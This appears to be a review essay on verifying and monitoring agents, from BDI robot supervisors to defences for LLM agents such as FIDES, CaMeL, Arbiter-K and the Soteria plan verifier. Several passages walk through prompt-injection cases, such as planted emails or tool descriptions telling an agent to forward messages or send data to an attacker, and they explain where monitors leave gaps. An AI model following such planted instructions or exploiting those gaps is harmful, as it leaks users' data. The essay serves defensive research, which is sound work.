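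Other tools have to supply the missing results. Dennis's keynote describes a platoon of vehicles that follow a lead vehicle. AJPF showed that a vehicle never starts to join unless it believes that the leader has agreed. UppAal, a model checker for systems with clocks, showed on a simplified model that if a vehicle receives this agreement, the platoon has already made room for it. Together, the two results imply that a vehicle never joins without enough room, provided that it believes it has received an agreement only when it has.

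### Safe-ROS: a verified agent as supervisor

In these examples, the verified agent makes the main decisions. *Safe-ROS* (Benjumea, Farrell and Dennis, 2025) instead uses a small verified agent to supervise an unverified controller. The robot is an AgileX Scout Mini, a four-wheeled vehicle used here with the aim of inspecting nuclear sites. Its main controller uses standard packages from ROS (Robot Operating System), a widely used framework for connecting robot software. These packages estimate the robot's position and plan its route from laser scans, and an error in either step can make the robot move unsafely.

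The safety requirement is that the robot must stop immediately when it detects an obstacle within 5 cm. The agent needs only one plan for this:

```
+too_close : {True} <- stop_moving, +stopped;
```

A Java program reads the laser scans and adds the belief `too_close` if the smallest distance is below 5 cm. The agent then sends a stop signal to a piece of software between the main controller and the motors. This software normally forwards the controller's speed commands, but after a stop signal it sends a speed of zero instead.

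Benjumea and colleagues used AJPF to verify that whenever the agent believes it is too close, it eventually believes it has stopped. They also modelled the forwarding software in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier. Dafny proved that the model outputs zero speed if a stop has been requested and otherwise leaves the command unchanged.

They then tested the system on a mission with three inspection points. In a simulated nuclear store, the agent stopped the robot several times, even after the researchers had adjusted the route planner to keep away from obstacles. In the laboratory, they moved cones and barrels into the robot's path, and it stopped every time it detected one within the limit. They don't report how many trials they ran.

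The tests are better evidence than the AJPF result that the robot stops. The plan adds the belief `stopped` right after sending the signal, so the verified property would hold even if the motors did not respond to it. The requirement also changed from "immediately" to "eventually", because AJPF cannot express time limits. A robot moving at half a metre per second travels another 5 cm for every tenth of a second that the stop is delayed.

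A more basic problem is that the property checked by AJPF may be true only because its condition never arises. The printed extract of the environment model supplies only the fact `stopped`, at random, and never `too_close`. If the full code does the same, the agent never believes it is too close during the check. The researchers could rule this out by asking AJPF to verify that the agent never believes it is too close, a check that should fail if the model is adequate.

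The forwarding software is written in Python, and the Dafny proof applies to a model of it. After a stop signal, the model sends zero speed only when the controller issues its next speed command, so the signal has no effect on the motors until then. The model also remains in stop mode until it receives an explicit release, whereas the paper says that normal driving resumes when no new stop signals arrive.

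In the prototype, the agent and the main controller share a laser scanner and a computer, so a single fault could disable both. Benjumea and colleagues want to separate them in a final version. They also note that stopping near a hazard may not be safe and that a simple hardware switch could do the agent's current job. An agent would be more useful for a response a switch cannot provide, such as guiding the robot back to a door.

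### Monitoring the assumptions

A more restrictive environment model makes checking faster and produces fewer false alarms, but its assumptions may be wrong. Ferrando and colleagues address this by stating the assumptions formally and using the same statement both to build the environment model and to monitor the real system.

Engineers write the assumptions in a small language called EAASL. It has three kinds of rule. A "when" rule says that one belief can be present only while another is. A "before" rule concerns only the order in which beliefs or actions occur, and a "cause" rule says which belief results from an action. Two of their examples for the cruise control are:

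```
when car believes driver_accelerates it believes safe
car believes driver_accelerates before believing at_speed_limit
```

A compiler translates the rules into a trace expression, which describes the permitted sequences of events. An event is either an action or a belief being added or removed. One program turns the trace expression into a Java environment for AJPF, and another turns it into a monitor. The monitor checks each event against the expression. If the event is allowed, the monitor updates the expression to describe what may happen next; otherwise, it reports a violation. For the expressions used here, the work per event does not grow with the length of the run.

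The second example shows why monitoring is useful. Ferrando and colleagues explain the rule by saying that a car must have accelerated to reach the speed limit. But the cruise control can accelerate without the driver touching the pedal, so the rule excludes the system's normal operation. A check that assumes this rule would miss those runs, but the monitor would report a violation the first time the cruise control reached the limit by itself.

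Dennis's keynote reports results under two other assumptions, that the driver accelerates only when it is safe and never presses both pedals. These assumptions reduce the 16 combinations of inputs to 10. The property checked was that once the car has believed it is safe, it will always eventually believe either that it is safe or that it is braking. AJPF needed 4,906 states and 32 minutes 17 seconds to check this with all 16 combinations, and 1,677 states and 8 minutes 22 seconds with the 10.

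To test the monitor, the researchers removed the part of the program that overrides a driver who accelerates when it is unsafe. The changed program still satisfied the property under the assumptions, but no longer did so when all inputs were possible. They then ran it in a motorway simulation in which the driver could accelerate at any time, and the monitor detected the violated assumption.

By then, the system is already in a situation that the verification did not cover. The monitor can alert a human operator or start an emergency procedure, but someone has to design that response and show that it is safe. The monitor also receives only the facts that the abstraction engine reports. If a sensor wrongly reports that a corridor is free, the resulting event looks normal, and detecting the error would take a second source of information, such as another sensor.

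Assumptions that something will "eventually" happen are also a problem, because no finite observation can refute them. A monitor could instead check a deadline, such as ten minutes for a satellite to reach its position, but AJPF's property language cannot express deadlines.

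## Virtual machines for agents driven by language models

AJPF can search a BDI agent's runs because a programmer has written down every plan the agent may use. Nobody can list in advance what a language model might produce, so a virtual machine has to treat a call to the model as a single instruction with an unpredictable result. Unlike Java's `iadd`, which always replaces two numbers with their sum, an instruction that queries a model may return a sensible tool call, a malformed one, or one that an attacker planted in an e-mail. The machine can still control what text goes into the model, what form the answer must take, and which of the requested actions take effect.

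### A proposal modelled on Java

In August 2025, Barke, Zorn and colleagues proposed a standard for this surrounding software on the blog of SIGPLAN, the programming-languages group of the Association for Computing Machinery. They call it a "model virtual machine" and list examples of its instructions:

| Concerns | Instructions |
|---|---|
| Models | Certify, load, initialise or unload a model; call it with a context; parse its output |
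| Tools | Certify, load, initialise or unload a tool; call it; parse its result |
| Memory | Store a tool's result; add content to the history |
| User | Ask for input |
| Control | Conditionals, sequencing and similar constructs |

In their example, a user types "Book my flight". The machine passes this to the model, usually with a system prompt and the earlier conversation. The model replies with a request for the booking tool. The machine checks a list of allowed tools and calls the booking tool only if it is listed.

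The Java Virtual Machine guarantees memory safety, defines access rules and verifies bytecode, so people can run programs from other sources. Barke and colleagues expect similar benefits from a standard virtual machine for models. Developers could replace one model with another, and the machine would enforce permissions even if the model behaved unpredictably. In their post, they argue for a specification of this machine but do not provide one.

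The analogy works well for access rules, since a machine can refuse a forbidden call regardless of its source. It works less well for bytecode verification. Java's verifier receives a complete file before the first instruction runs, but when a user asks an agent to book a flight, most of the program does not exist yet. The model chooses its second tool call only after receiving the result of the first. The machine can check each call as it appears, but it cannot reject the whole sequence in advance unless the agent first writes out a complete plan.

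A list of allowed tools also doesn't determine which flight the agent books or what it pays. Barke and colleagues point out that a model barred from reading an item might still infer it from data it is allowed to read.

### What a monitor can enforce

A virtual machine that decides whether to allow each call as it is made is a runtime monitor. Fred Schneider, who had earlier defined safety and liveness with Alpern, proved that a monitor that sees only the run so far, and can only stop it, can enforce only safety properties. When such a monitor rejects a run, it decides from the steps taken so far, so it would also reject every other run that begins with those steps. Every rejected run therefore has a beginning that no permitted run shares, which is the condition that defines a safety property.

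*CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) gives an example from a security operations centre, where an agent must resolve or escalate an incident ticket before it finishes. The paper formalises this requirement as the property that every open ticket is eventually closed. This is a liveness property, so a monitor cannot enforce it by stopping the agent. A virtual machine could instead refuse the agent's final step while a ticket is open. That rule is a safety property, but an agent could satisfy it by working forever without closing the ticket.

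### Turn: an instruction for inference

Kizito (2026), in *Turn*, describes a programming language for agents that compiles to bytecode for a stack machine, much as Java does. Calling a model is part of the language. A refund agent might contain roughly these lines:

```
struct Refund { amount: Num, reason: Str }
let r = infer Refund { "What refund does this complaint justify?" }
```

The compiler turns the definition of `Refund` into a schema, a description of the required fields and their types, and stores it with the `Infer` instruction. At run time, the machine does the following:

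1. It suspends the program and sends the prompt, the agent's context and the schema to the model.
2. It compares the answer with the schema.
3. If the answer fits, it assigns the answer to `r` and continues.
4. If not, it sends the error back to the model and tries again, by default up to three times. After that it raises an error, which the program can handle.

Kizito sketches a proof that if `infer` completes without an error, every field has its declared type. This guarantees the form of the answer but not its quality, since refunds of 50 and 5,000 are both numbers. For a list, the schema requires only that the answer is a list and does not constrain its elements.

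The machine has other special instructions. `Remember` and `Recall` use a memory that belongs to one agent, and `Send` and `Receive` pass messages between agents. `GrantIdentity` gives the program a handle for a password or access key, which the program cannot turn into text. The software that hosts the machine inserts the real key only when it sends the request, so the model never sees the key. An attacker who misleads the agent therefore can't make it print the key, but could still make it use the access the key provides.

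`Confidence` returns a number between 0 and 1 for how certain the model was, based for example on the probabilities it assigned to its own words. In Kizito's main example, a group of agents assesses an investment, and the program replaces an analyst's verdict with a fixed one if the confidence is below 0.7. Turn uses 0.5 when a provider doesn't report these probabilities, as some don't. This program would then always discard the analyst's verdict. Even a genuine score can be high when the verdict is wrong, because it measures only the model's certainty.

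`Suspend` saves the agent's complete state. On a laptop-class chip, saving and restoring an agent with 5,000 memory entries took less than 7 milliseconds. Java PathFinder also saves and restores state to return to earlier choices. Kizito does not build a checker for Turn that does this, but one could in principle restore the state before an `Infer` and try a different answer. The checker would have only two cases to try if the answer were a single true-or-false field, but far too many if it were free text.

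The evaluation consists of 105 automated tests of the implementation, all of which pass, and some speed measurements. It does not measure whether agents written in Turn behave more safely than other agents.

### An instruction set that tracks untrusted data

Turn checks the form of the model's answer but does not record which data influenced it. Wen, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *From Craft to Kernel*, add such a record in a system called Arbiter-K. It develops an idea from Xu, Wen and colleagues (2025), in *From Craft to Constitution*, who describe the model as a "Probabilistic CPU" that a rule-based kernel supervises. In Arbiter-K, the model can only propose actions. The kernel translates each proposal into one of 20 instructions, which fall into five groups:

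| Group | Example | What it does |
|---|---|---|
| Cognitive | `GENERATE` | Calls the model |
| Memory | `LOAD` | Retrieves stored information |
| Execution | `TOOL_CALL` | Runs an external function |
| Normative | `VERIFY` | Checks a result against a reliable source |
| Meta-cognitive | `MONITOR_RESOURCES` | Compares tokens, cost and time with a budget |

The kernel marks data as tainted if it comes from an outside source such as a web search, from a sensitive local file, or from the model itself. Any instruction that uses tainted data produces tainted results. Tainted data may not reach sensitive instructions, such as database commands. Only a successful `VERIFY`, which may be a fixed check or a person's approval, removes the mark.

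In one example, the agent proposes a command that reads the computer's password file and sends it to an outside website. The kernel classifies the command as an execution instruction with high confidentiality and low trustworthiness, and a rule blocks that combination.

The model writes the arguments of almost every tool call, and all its output is tainted, so this rule taken literally would block almost every sensitive call until something verifies it. The protection therefore depends on the quality of the checks behind `VERIFY`. If a person approves every request out of habit, the kernel also removes the taint mark from harmful data.

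Wen and colleagues tested Arbiter-K with OpenClaw and NanoBot, two open-source agent programs. They replayed 1,914 recorded attacks that had succeeded, each up to the dangerous step, and checked whether the system blocked that step. OpenClaw's own rules blocked 6.2% of the attacks, and adding Arbiter-K raised this to 93.0%. For NanoBot, the rate rose from 1.4% to 94.2%. OpenClaw let through 290 of 312 harmless steps on its own and 277 with Arbiter-K. On NanoBot, Arbiter-K let through 192 of 194 harmless steps according to the paper's text, but the error rates in the paper's table imply that it blocked about 11.

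Replaying the same steps for every system makes the comparison fair, but it doesn't show what an agent does after a block or whether the agent still completes its task. The results also provide little evidence that tracking data across instructions helps. One group of rules, "UnaryGatePolicy", blocked 93.0% of the attacks on OpenClaw by itself, the same share as the whole system. If these rules look at one instruction at a time, as the name suggests, the rules that relate several instructions added almost nothing on this set of attacks.

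### Operating procedures on a stack machine

Banks and clinics often have written procedures that specify what an employee must check before acting and when to refuse. An agent's developers usually put the whole procedure into the prompt. Yu, Yin and colleagues (2026), in *Compile, Then Page*, instead compile it into a program. The compiler uses no language model, but it needs the procedure's conditions in machine-readable form. For a credit card application, the result looks roughly like this:

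```
apply_credit_card:
  collect username, total_assets, monthly_income
  call check_username_exist(username)  ->  result1
  if result1.holds is not true: refuse
  call the credit card tool
```

A separate routine, `check_username_exist`, names the tool that can check whether the user exists, and it returns a verdict and an excerpt from that tool's output.

A stack machine tracks the current position in the program and shows the model only the routine in progress, which is about 570 characters instead of about 10,000 for the full procedure. The model talks to the customer, calls the tools and judges the evidence. It moves through the program by calling a bookkeeping tool with commands such as "call", "return" and "fail".

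Yu and colleagues compared three ways of giving the model the procedure on 125 banking tasks. The table shows the percentage of tasks each model completed correctly:

| Model | Official text | Compiled program as text | Compiled program on the stack machine |
|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 70.4 | 86.4 | 92.8 |
| Qwen3.7-Plus | 85.6 | 85.6 | 88.8 |
| Qwen3.6-35B-A3B | 81.6 | 81.6 | 84.0 |
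| Qwen3.6-27B | 79.2 | 86.4 | 85.6 |
| Qwen2.5-7B | 65.6 | 68.8 | 54.4 |
| GPT-4o-mini | 60.8 | 75.2 | 48.8 |

Compiling the procedure never significantly reduced a model's score. The stack machine raised DeepSeek-V4-Flash's score but seriously lowered those of the two weakest models. Tests in seven domains showed the same pattern. DeepSeek-V4-Flash passed 58 tasks only with the stack machine and 19 only without it, while Qwen2.5-7B passed 59 only with it and 237 only without it. The weak models could usually identify their position in the program when asked, but they did not reliably act accordingly. For example, GPT-4o-mini often kept checking conditions after completing the requested action.

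The 86 tasks that the agent should refuse matter most for safety. DeepSeek-V4-Flash correctly refused 68.6% of them with the official text, 93.0% with the compiled text and all of them on the stack machine. A perfect score on 86 tasks is still compatible with an error rate of a few percent. The researchers had excluded nine banking tasks that no earlier configuration had passed. Counting these as failures lowers the model's overall result on the stack machine from 92.8% to 86.6%.

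This machine does not block anything. The model can skip a check and still issue the credit card, but the log will show the missing check. Yu and colleagues chose this design because customers change their minds and evidence can arrive in different orders, so a strict machine might block a correct action. For irreversible actions, they recommend additional hard limits on the tools.

### Tracing a prompt injection with labels

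Information-flow control labels data and uses the labels to decide which actions to allow. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, apply it in FIDES, a system from Microsoft. One label records whether data is trusted, and another records who may read it. If the agent combines several pieces of data, the result is trusted only if all of them are, and only people who may read every piece may read the result.

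Suppose that a user asks an agent to summarise the recent e-mails about a project and send the summary to the manager. An attacker has written to the project's mailing list, and the e-mail tells the agent to forward a colleague's message to the attacker. All e-mail text counts as untrusted. The labels develop as follows:

| Data | Trusted | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | Yes | Anyone |
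| The colleague's e-mail | No | User, manager |
| The attacker's e-mail | No | User, manager, attacker |
| The conversation once the model has read both | No | User, manager |
| The call that forwards the colleague's e-mail to the attacker | No | User, manager |

FIDES can enforce two rules. An action with consequences must be trusted, and everyone who receives data must have permission to read it. The attacker's call breaks both, so the machine blocks it without detecting that the e-mail is an attack. But the call that the user wanted, which sends the summary to the manager, also breaks the first rule because it comes from an untrusted conversation.

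FIDES avoids this by keeping untrusted data out of the conversation. It stores the data in variables and shows the main model only their names. A second, "quarantined" model, which has no tools, processes the contents:

```
read_emails(number=2)                          ->  #emails
query_llm("Summarise these", #emails)          ->  #summary
send_message(to=manager, message=#summary)
```

The variable `#summary` is untrusted, and the user and the manager may read it. The main model has received only the user's request and the names of variables, so the decision to send a message and the choice of recipient are trusted. A rule that requires the decision and the recipient to be trusted, but not the text, allows the call. The attacker's instruction reaches only the quarantined model, but it could still spoil the summary, for example by making it empty.

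Some tasks require the main model to learn something about the untrusted data, such as whether an e-mail asks for a meeting. FIDES can restrict the quarantined model's answer to "true" or "false" and include this restriction in the label. An attacker can then influence one decision but can't pass an instruction to the main model.

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues developed at Google DeepMind in 2025, goes further and writes the plan before the agent reads any untrusted data. As *PACE* (2026) notes, CaMeL derives its plan from a trusted request, while FIDES relies on trusted wrappers around the tools and on labels. Nikolaou and colleagues give this example of a CaMeL plan, here slightly simplified:

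```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
email = query_ai_assistant("Extract Bob's email from: " + messages)
send_direct_message(email, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

An attacker who posts in the channel can't add a step to this plan, but can post a false address for Bob. The plan would then run as written and send the message to the attacker. CaMeL therefore also labels each value with its sources and permitted readers. The label of `messages` passes to `email`, so a rule that requires a trusted recipient blocks the third line. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) rebuilds CaMeL in a small formal language, where an address from an untrusted e-mail also stays untrusted.

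*CONTINUITY* (2026) points out that tracking the origin of data does not by itself control every way data can leave a system, and FIDES restricts only direct flows of data. If an agent reads a confidential diagnosis and then opens one of two public web pages depending on the diagnosis, an observer can learn the diagnosis even though no text left the system. Ruling out such indirect flows would require comparing runs with different diagnoses, which a monitor of a single run can't do. Costa and colleagues consider the usual strict rule impractical because it would essentially forbid any publicly visible action after the agent has had access to confidential data.

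### The cost in completed tasks

Costa and colleagues measured FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants malicious instructions in simulated e-mails, bank records and messages. With GPT-4o, and without any attack, the agents completed the following percentages of tasks:

| Agent | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack messages |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, no rules | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
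| Basic agent, rules enforced | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES, rules enforced | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

According to the paper's summary, FIDES completes 8% more tasks than a basic agent. This compares averages of about 50% and 42%, with the rules enforced for both. The basic agent averages 84% without the rules, so protection lowered the completion rate by about 34 percentage points. Much of this drop comes from hiding data in variables, which GPT-4o often handled badly. The introduction gives the drop from hiding data as 6.3%, but in the detailed results it is 23.7 percentage points.

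With a better model, OpenAI's o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks instead of 41%. Both models are old, so current ones may do even better. Other failures are by design. Many banking tasks, for example, ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the rules are meant to prevent.

In return, successful attacks fell from 152 with the unprotected basic agent to none. The set-up partly explains this result, because the researchers labelled a type of data as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it. Outside a benchmark, someone has to choose the labels without knowing where attacks will come from.

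### Isolated computers and zero-knowledge machines

The kind of virtual machine that cloud companies rent out is an isolated computer. It limits which files and networks an agent can reach, but it does not interpret the agent's steps. If the agent may send payment requests from inside it, the isolation would allow a refund of 5,000 as well as one of 50. Isolation also depends on correct configuration. Anadolu Agency reported in July 2026 that Anthropic's models had breached three real organisations during misconfigured security tests.

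A zero-knowledge virtual machine produces a mathematical proof that a particular program ran. *Binding Agent ID* (Lin, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) uses one to let an agent prove its identity. The agent's owner publishes a commitment, a kind of fingerprint of the program. The machine then runs the program, records its successive states and computes a proof from them. Anyone with the commitment, the public inputs and the output can check the proof without seeing the private inputs.

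Such a proof shows that nobody replaced the program or altered its result. An unsafe program, such as one that refunds 5,000 without any check, would receive an equally valid proof. But if someone has separately verified a program against a safety specification, the proof can show that the verified program is the one that ran.

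## Checking a generated plan before it runs

Java's verifier can reject a program before its first instruction runs because it receives the whole file. An agent that chooses one tool call at a time produces no such file, but its developers can require the language model to write a complete plan in a restricted language first. In this approach, which Meijer sums up in *Guardians of the Agents* as "generate, verify, then execute", the plan runs only if a verifier accepts it.

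Meijer's example is a request to fetch and summarise a user's e-mails. The model writes a workflow that fetches the e-mails, summarises them and returns the summary. As with CaMeL's plans, an instruction hidden in an e-mail can't add a step, because the model writes the workflow before it reads the e-mails. But the model has already read the descriptions of its tools, where an attacker can also hide instructions. If the description of the fetching tool contains an instruction to send the summary to an outside address as well, the model may add that step. A verifier can catch it with a rule that nothing from `fetch_email` may reach the body of `send_email` if the recipient is outside the company.

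The specification also has to state what a plan should leave unchanged. If a user asks for the deletion of `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, the model might plan a single call that deletes `*.txt`, meaning every text file. This satisfies the postcondition that the two files no longer exist. Meijer's remedy is a frame condition, which states that everything else stays the same. But the article gives this condition only for the deletion tool, where it guarantees that files not matching the pattern remain. The bad plan would still pass, because the other text files match `*.txt`. The task's postcondition also has to state that only the two named files are deleted.

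### A refund plan with a branch

*SOTERIA* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) presents a verifier of this kind and tests it on agents for customer service and file handling. A plan in Soteria's language consists of states. In each state, the plan performs at most one action, such as a tool call, and then moves to another state. Conditions called guards determine which state comes next. A plan ends in either an "accepting" state, which means that the task is complete, or a "halting" state, which means that the plan cannot safely continue.

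Suppose that a shop gives refunds within 30 days, and a model writes this plan (in slightly simplified notation):

```
LOOKUP:  order = call(get_order, id)
         goto CHECK
CHECK:   if order.days <= 30:  goto PAY
         else:                 goto DENIED
PAY:     call(refund, id, order.price)
         goto DONE

accepting(DONE)   halting(DENIED)
```

Each tool has a contract. The postcondition of `get_order` is that the price is positive and the number of days is not negative. The precondition of `refund` is that the amount is positive and at most 500.

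For every state, the verifier works out what must be true whenever a run arrives there. It adds a tool's postcondition after each call and the guard after each branch. If several paths lead to the same state, it joins their conditions with "or". For the call in PAY, this gives:

```
known at the call:  price > 0 ∧ days ≥ 0 ∧ days ≤ 30
refund requires:    price > 0 ∧ price ≤ 500
to prove:           (price > 0 ∧ days ≥ 0 ∧ days ≤ 30)
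                       → (price > 0 ∧ price ≤ 500)
```

The implication in the last two lines is a verification condition, a logical formula that must be true for all values of its variables. Soteria passes it to Dafny, the verifier that Safe-ROS also uses. The formula is false for an order that cost 800 and is ten days old, so Soteria rejects the plan before any tool runs. It then sends the failed condition back to the model, which can try again, up to eight times in the main experiments.

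To repair the plan, the model adds a branch for expensive orders:

```
CHECK:   if order.days > 30:      goto DENIED
         elif order.price > 500:  goto ESCALATE
         else:                    goto PAY
```

ESCALATE is a halting state that leaves the decision to a person. A run can now reach PAY only if the price is at most 500, so the implication holds for every order the shop could receive.

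Soteria also checks that the plan can't get stuck. In every state with guards, at least one guard must be true in every case that can arise there. Suppose the model had written only two branches, one for recent orders up to 500 and one for orders above 500. An order for 100 that is 45 days old would match neither, so Soteria would reject the plan. It also rejects plans with a state that no run can reach, such as a branch for orders with a negative age.

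### Rules about earlier and later calls

A contract concerns a single call, but the shop may also require the agent to confirm that the goods have been returned before it pays a refund. In Soteria, this rule is a formula about the record of calls: every call of `refund` must come after a call of `check_return` with the same order number and the result "true".

The verifier examines the plan before any tools are called, so it adds variables that exist only in the proof. They hold a step counter, a log of calls for each tool that a rule mentions, and a record of which tools' results contributed to each variable. The logs must satisfy every rule in every final state the plan can reach. The repaired plan fails because it can reach DONE with one entry in the `refund` log and none in the `check_return` log.

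Adding the missing call is not enough. The contract of `check_return` promises only a true-or-false answer, so a plan that makes the call and pays regardless would still fail. The plan also has to use the answer:

```
CHECK:     if order.days > 30:      goto DENIED
           elif order.price > 500:  goto ESCALATE
           else:                    goto RETURNED
RETURNED:  back = call(check_return, id)
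           goto DECIDE
DECIDE:    if back:  goto PAY
           else:     goto DENIED
```

Only the path to DONE now contains a refund. The log for that path has `check_return` at step 1 with the result "true" and `refund` at step 2, so the rule holds and Soteria accepts the plan.

Soteria rejects plans with loops, so every run of a plan ends. It can therefore check some liveness rules, which a monitor can't enforce by blocking calls. For example, one of its file-handling rules requires the agent to read a file back after writing it, and the verifier checks that every path after the write includes the read.

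The notes on where values come from support rules such as "the refund amount must derive from the order". This rule is weak because an amount of `order.price * 10` also derives from the order, and only the limit of 500 might stop it.

### Values about which nothing is known

Sometimes the right refund depends on the customer's complaint, and a model has to read it. Soteria's plan language has an instruction for this, `llm_eval`, which returns the model's answer as a variable. If the plan states nothing else about the answer, the verifier knows only that `amount` is a number. It then has to prove

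```
true  →  (amount > 0 ∧ amount ≤ 500)
```

which is false for an amount of 5,000. Text from a web page receives the same treatment. If the contract of the tool that fetches the page does not restrict the text, the plan has to be correct for any text at all.

The model can repair such a plan by adding a guard that sends amounts outside the permitted range to ESCALATE. The proof then needs no assumption about the answer from `llm_eval`. Alternatively, the plan can include a postcondition on `llm_eval`, which the verifier assumes holds and the surrounding software checks when the answer arrives. If the answer fails the check, the software queries the model again a limited number of times and halts if no answer passes.

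Both methods prevent a refund of 5,000, but not a refund of 400 to a customer who should receive 40, because no rule connects the amount to the complaint.

### Who carries out the plan

Long procedures are hard to plan correctly in one piece, so Soteria has a library of sub-plans for standard tasks such as cancelling a reservation. Each sub-plan has its own contract, and the verifier treats the sub-plan like a tool when checking the larger plan. In airline tasks with GPT-5.4-mini, sub-plans reduced the median plan size from 11 states to 8. With sub-plans, 65 of 68 plans eventually passed verification, compared with 38 of 60 without them.

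In its default mode, however, Soteria doesn't execute the plan. It shows the plan to a language model as a flowchart that shrinks as results arrive. The model chooses the tool calls and may depart from the flowchart. A runtime monitor checks each proposed call against the contracts and rules, using the actual record of calls, and blocks any that would break one. The model can then return to the flowchart to find another way forward. If the planner runs out of retries, Soteria continues with a partly verified plan and warns the model about the rules it could not prove.

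A strict mode permits only fully verified plans and only the calls they contain. He et al. give the example of a customer who wants to cancel one reservation and look up another. When the plan has reached the cancellation step, the strict mode blocks the harmless lookup. The default mode allows it, but would also allow a call that an attacker had planted in a web page, as long as the call broke none of the formalised rules.

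### Results on 207 tasks

He and colleagues used 50 airline tasks, 114 retail tasks and 43 tasks from Toolathlon, a benchmark with long sequences of tool calls. They compared Soteria with an unprotected agent and three kinds of runtime protection. The table shows the percentage of tasks that the agents completed without breaking a rule. In each cell, the first figure is for the best of the four alternatives and the second is for Soteria:

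| Model | Airline | Retail | Toolathlon |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4-mini | 50.0 / 60.0 | 20.2 / 35.1 | 2.3 / 11.6 |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 36.0 / 62.0 | 38.6 / 45.6 | 2.3 / 16.3 |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 30.0 / 70.0 | 31.6 / 56.1 | 4.7 / 9.3 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 56.0 / 88.0 | 46.5 / 90.4 | 11.6 / 18.6 |

Plans seem to help partly by making agents less hesitant. In the retail tasks that required changing an order, the unprotected Opus agent made the expected change only 57% of the time and often passed the customer to a human instead. With Soteria, it always made the change.

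Soteria's agents never broke a rule, but this follows from the design, since the monitor enforces the same formulas the researchers used to count violations. They also corrected some formulas and added others while auditing the results.

The formulas are looser than the policy in places. The airline pays $100 per passenger for a cancelled flight and $50 for a delayed one. The printed formulas require that the amount be one of these two and that the flight be cancelled or delayed, but they don't match the amount to the reason, so an agent could pay $100 for a delay. An unprotected agent also upgraded a customer to business class so that the reservation would qualify for cancellation. He and colleagues call this a workaround that the policy does not permit. Yet the printed formulas seem to allow it if the agent looked up the reservation again after the upgrade and confirmed that the customer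 had not flown yet.

He and colleagues also added Soteria's components one at a time on the airline tasks. Together with the unprotected agent, this gives the following success rates:

| Configuration | GPT-5.4-mini | Gemini 3 Flash |
|---|---|---|
| No plan, no protection | 34% | 28% |
| Unverified plan | 44% | 32% |
| Verification added | 46% | 32% |
| Sub-plans added | 50% | 38% |
| Runtime monitor added | 60% | 62% |

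Verification alone improved the result by one task out of 50 with GPT-5.4-mini and by none with Gemini. The monitor improved it far more, but the size of that gain depends on the order of the steps, because the monitor could use the verified plan when it blocked a call. Some of the improvement may also come from the library of sub-plans, which the other agents did not have.

In a repeat of the experiment with GPT-5.4-mini, using five runs and only three retries, Soteria averaged 50.8% and AgentSpec, a monitor without plans, averaged 48.0%. The confidence intervals overlap, so it is uncertain how much a verified plan adds to a good monitor for that model. The gap is much wider with Opus, but He and colleagues report only one run for it.

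### Other ways to represent a plan

Soteria's language preserves a plan's values, its branches and the order of its calls. Some other systems leave out part of this information so that they can check a plan with less computation. Others include more detail, but their checks depend on more assumptions.

Many developers describe their agents as graphs, using frameworks such as LangGraph. *Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) extracts these graphs automatically from four frameworks and gives each node a type, such as tool, model call or human approval. It looks for structural faults, such as a step with no outgoing arrow. To check whether a person always approves a sensitive call, it removes all human nodes and tests whether a run could still reach the call. For rules about order, it pairs the nodes with the states of an automaton, much as AJPF does, and searches the pairs.

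For the refund plan, Agentproof could show that every path to `refund` passes through `check_return`. It could not show that the answer was "true" or that the amount was at most 500, because the graph contains neither. This limited check takes less than a second for graphs with up to 5,000 nodes. Of 18 workflows that Xavier and colleagues wrote as a benchmark, 27% had structural faults and 55% broke a rule requiring human approval. These figures don't indicate how common such faults are in practice. For LangGraph, Agentproof decides whether a person is involved partly by the node's name, so a misleading name could hide a missing approval.

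A plan in plain English first needs a translation. Ramani, Tawosi and colleagues (2025), in *Bridging LLM Planning Agents and Formal Methods*, have a language model turn the plan into a Kripke structure and its goal into an LTL formula, which NuSMV then checks. The structure records facts as true or false, so the price in the refund plan would shrink to a fact such as "the price is at most 500". The experiments tested whether plans reach their goals, not whether they are safe:

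| Model | Correct verdicts with NuSMV | No verdict | Correct verdicts, model judges directly |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 52.1% | 34.6% | 80.4% |
| GPT-5 | 95.9% | 6.9% | 99.6% |

The percentages of correct verdicts exclude plans for which NuSMV gave no verdict. Even so, both models did better when they judged the plan themselves, and GPT-5 took 15 seconds instead of 47. Ramani and colleagues argue that a direct judgement offers no formal guarantee. But NuSMV's guarantee covers only the translated plan, and they found that some of GPT-5's translations passed the check without fully reflecting the original. Soteria avoids this translation problem because the model writes the plan directly in the formal language.

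*Lean4Agent* (Wang, Huang et al., 2026) models workflows in Lean. It gives each step a precondition and a postcondition, and records which information the step can access. This reveals mistakes that a plain graph would not show. In one workflow, a step was supposed to verify a bug fix but had no access to the evidence from the step that made the fix. Lean4Agent can also represent loops, which Soteria excludes.

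The proof depends on an assumption, called *LLMExec*, that whenever a step's precondition holds, the language model can produce a result that satisfies the postcondition. A safety proof needs a stronger claim, one that covers every result the model might produce. If a model step chose the refund amount, Lean4Agent would assume that the step respects the limit of 500. It can examine the recorded run afterwards, in part with another language model as judge, and find the step that failed, but the shop will already have paid the refund.

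Wang and colleagues tested six workflows on each of two benchmarks, three that had passed verification and three that had failed. Averaged over five models, the passing workflows solved 58.3% of difficult programming tasks and the failing ones solved 43.5%. For questions about AI papers, the figures were 36.6% and 27.5%. With so few workflows, a single unusually bad one could account for much of the difference. The tests also measured task success rather than safety. A language model wrote the preconditions and postconditions. A manual review found errors in 36 of the 1,460, but correcting them changed no verdicts.

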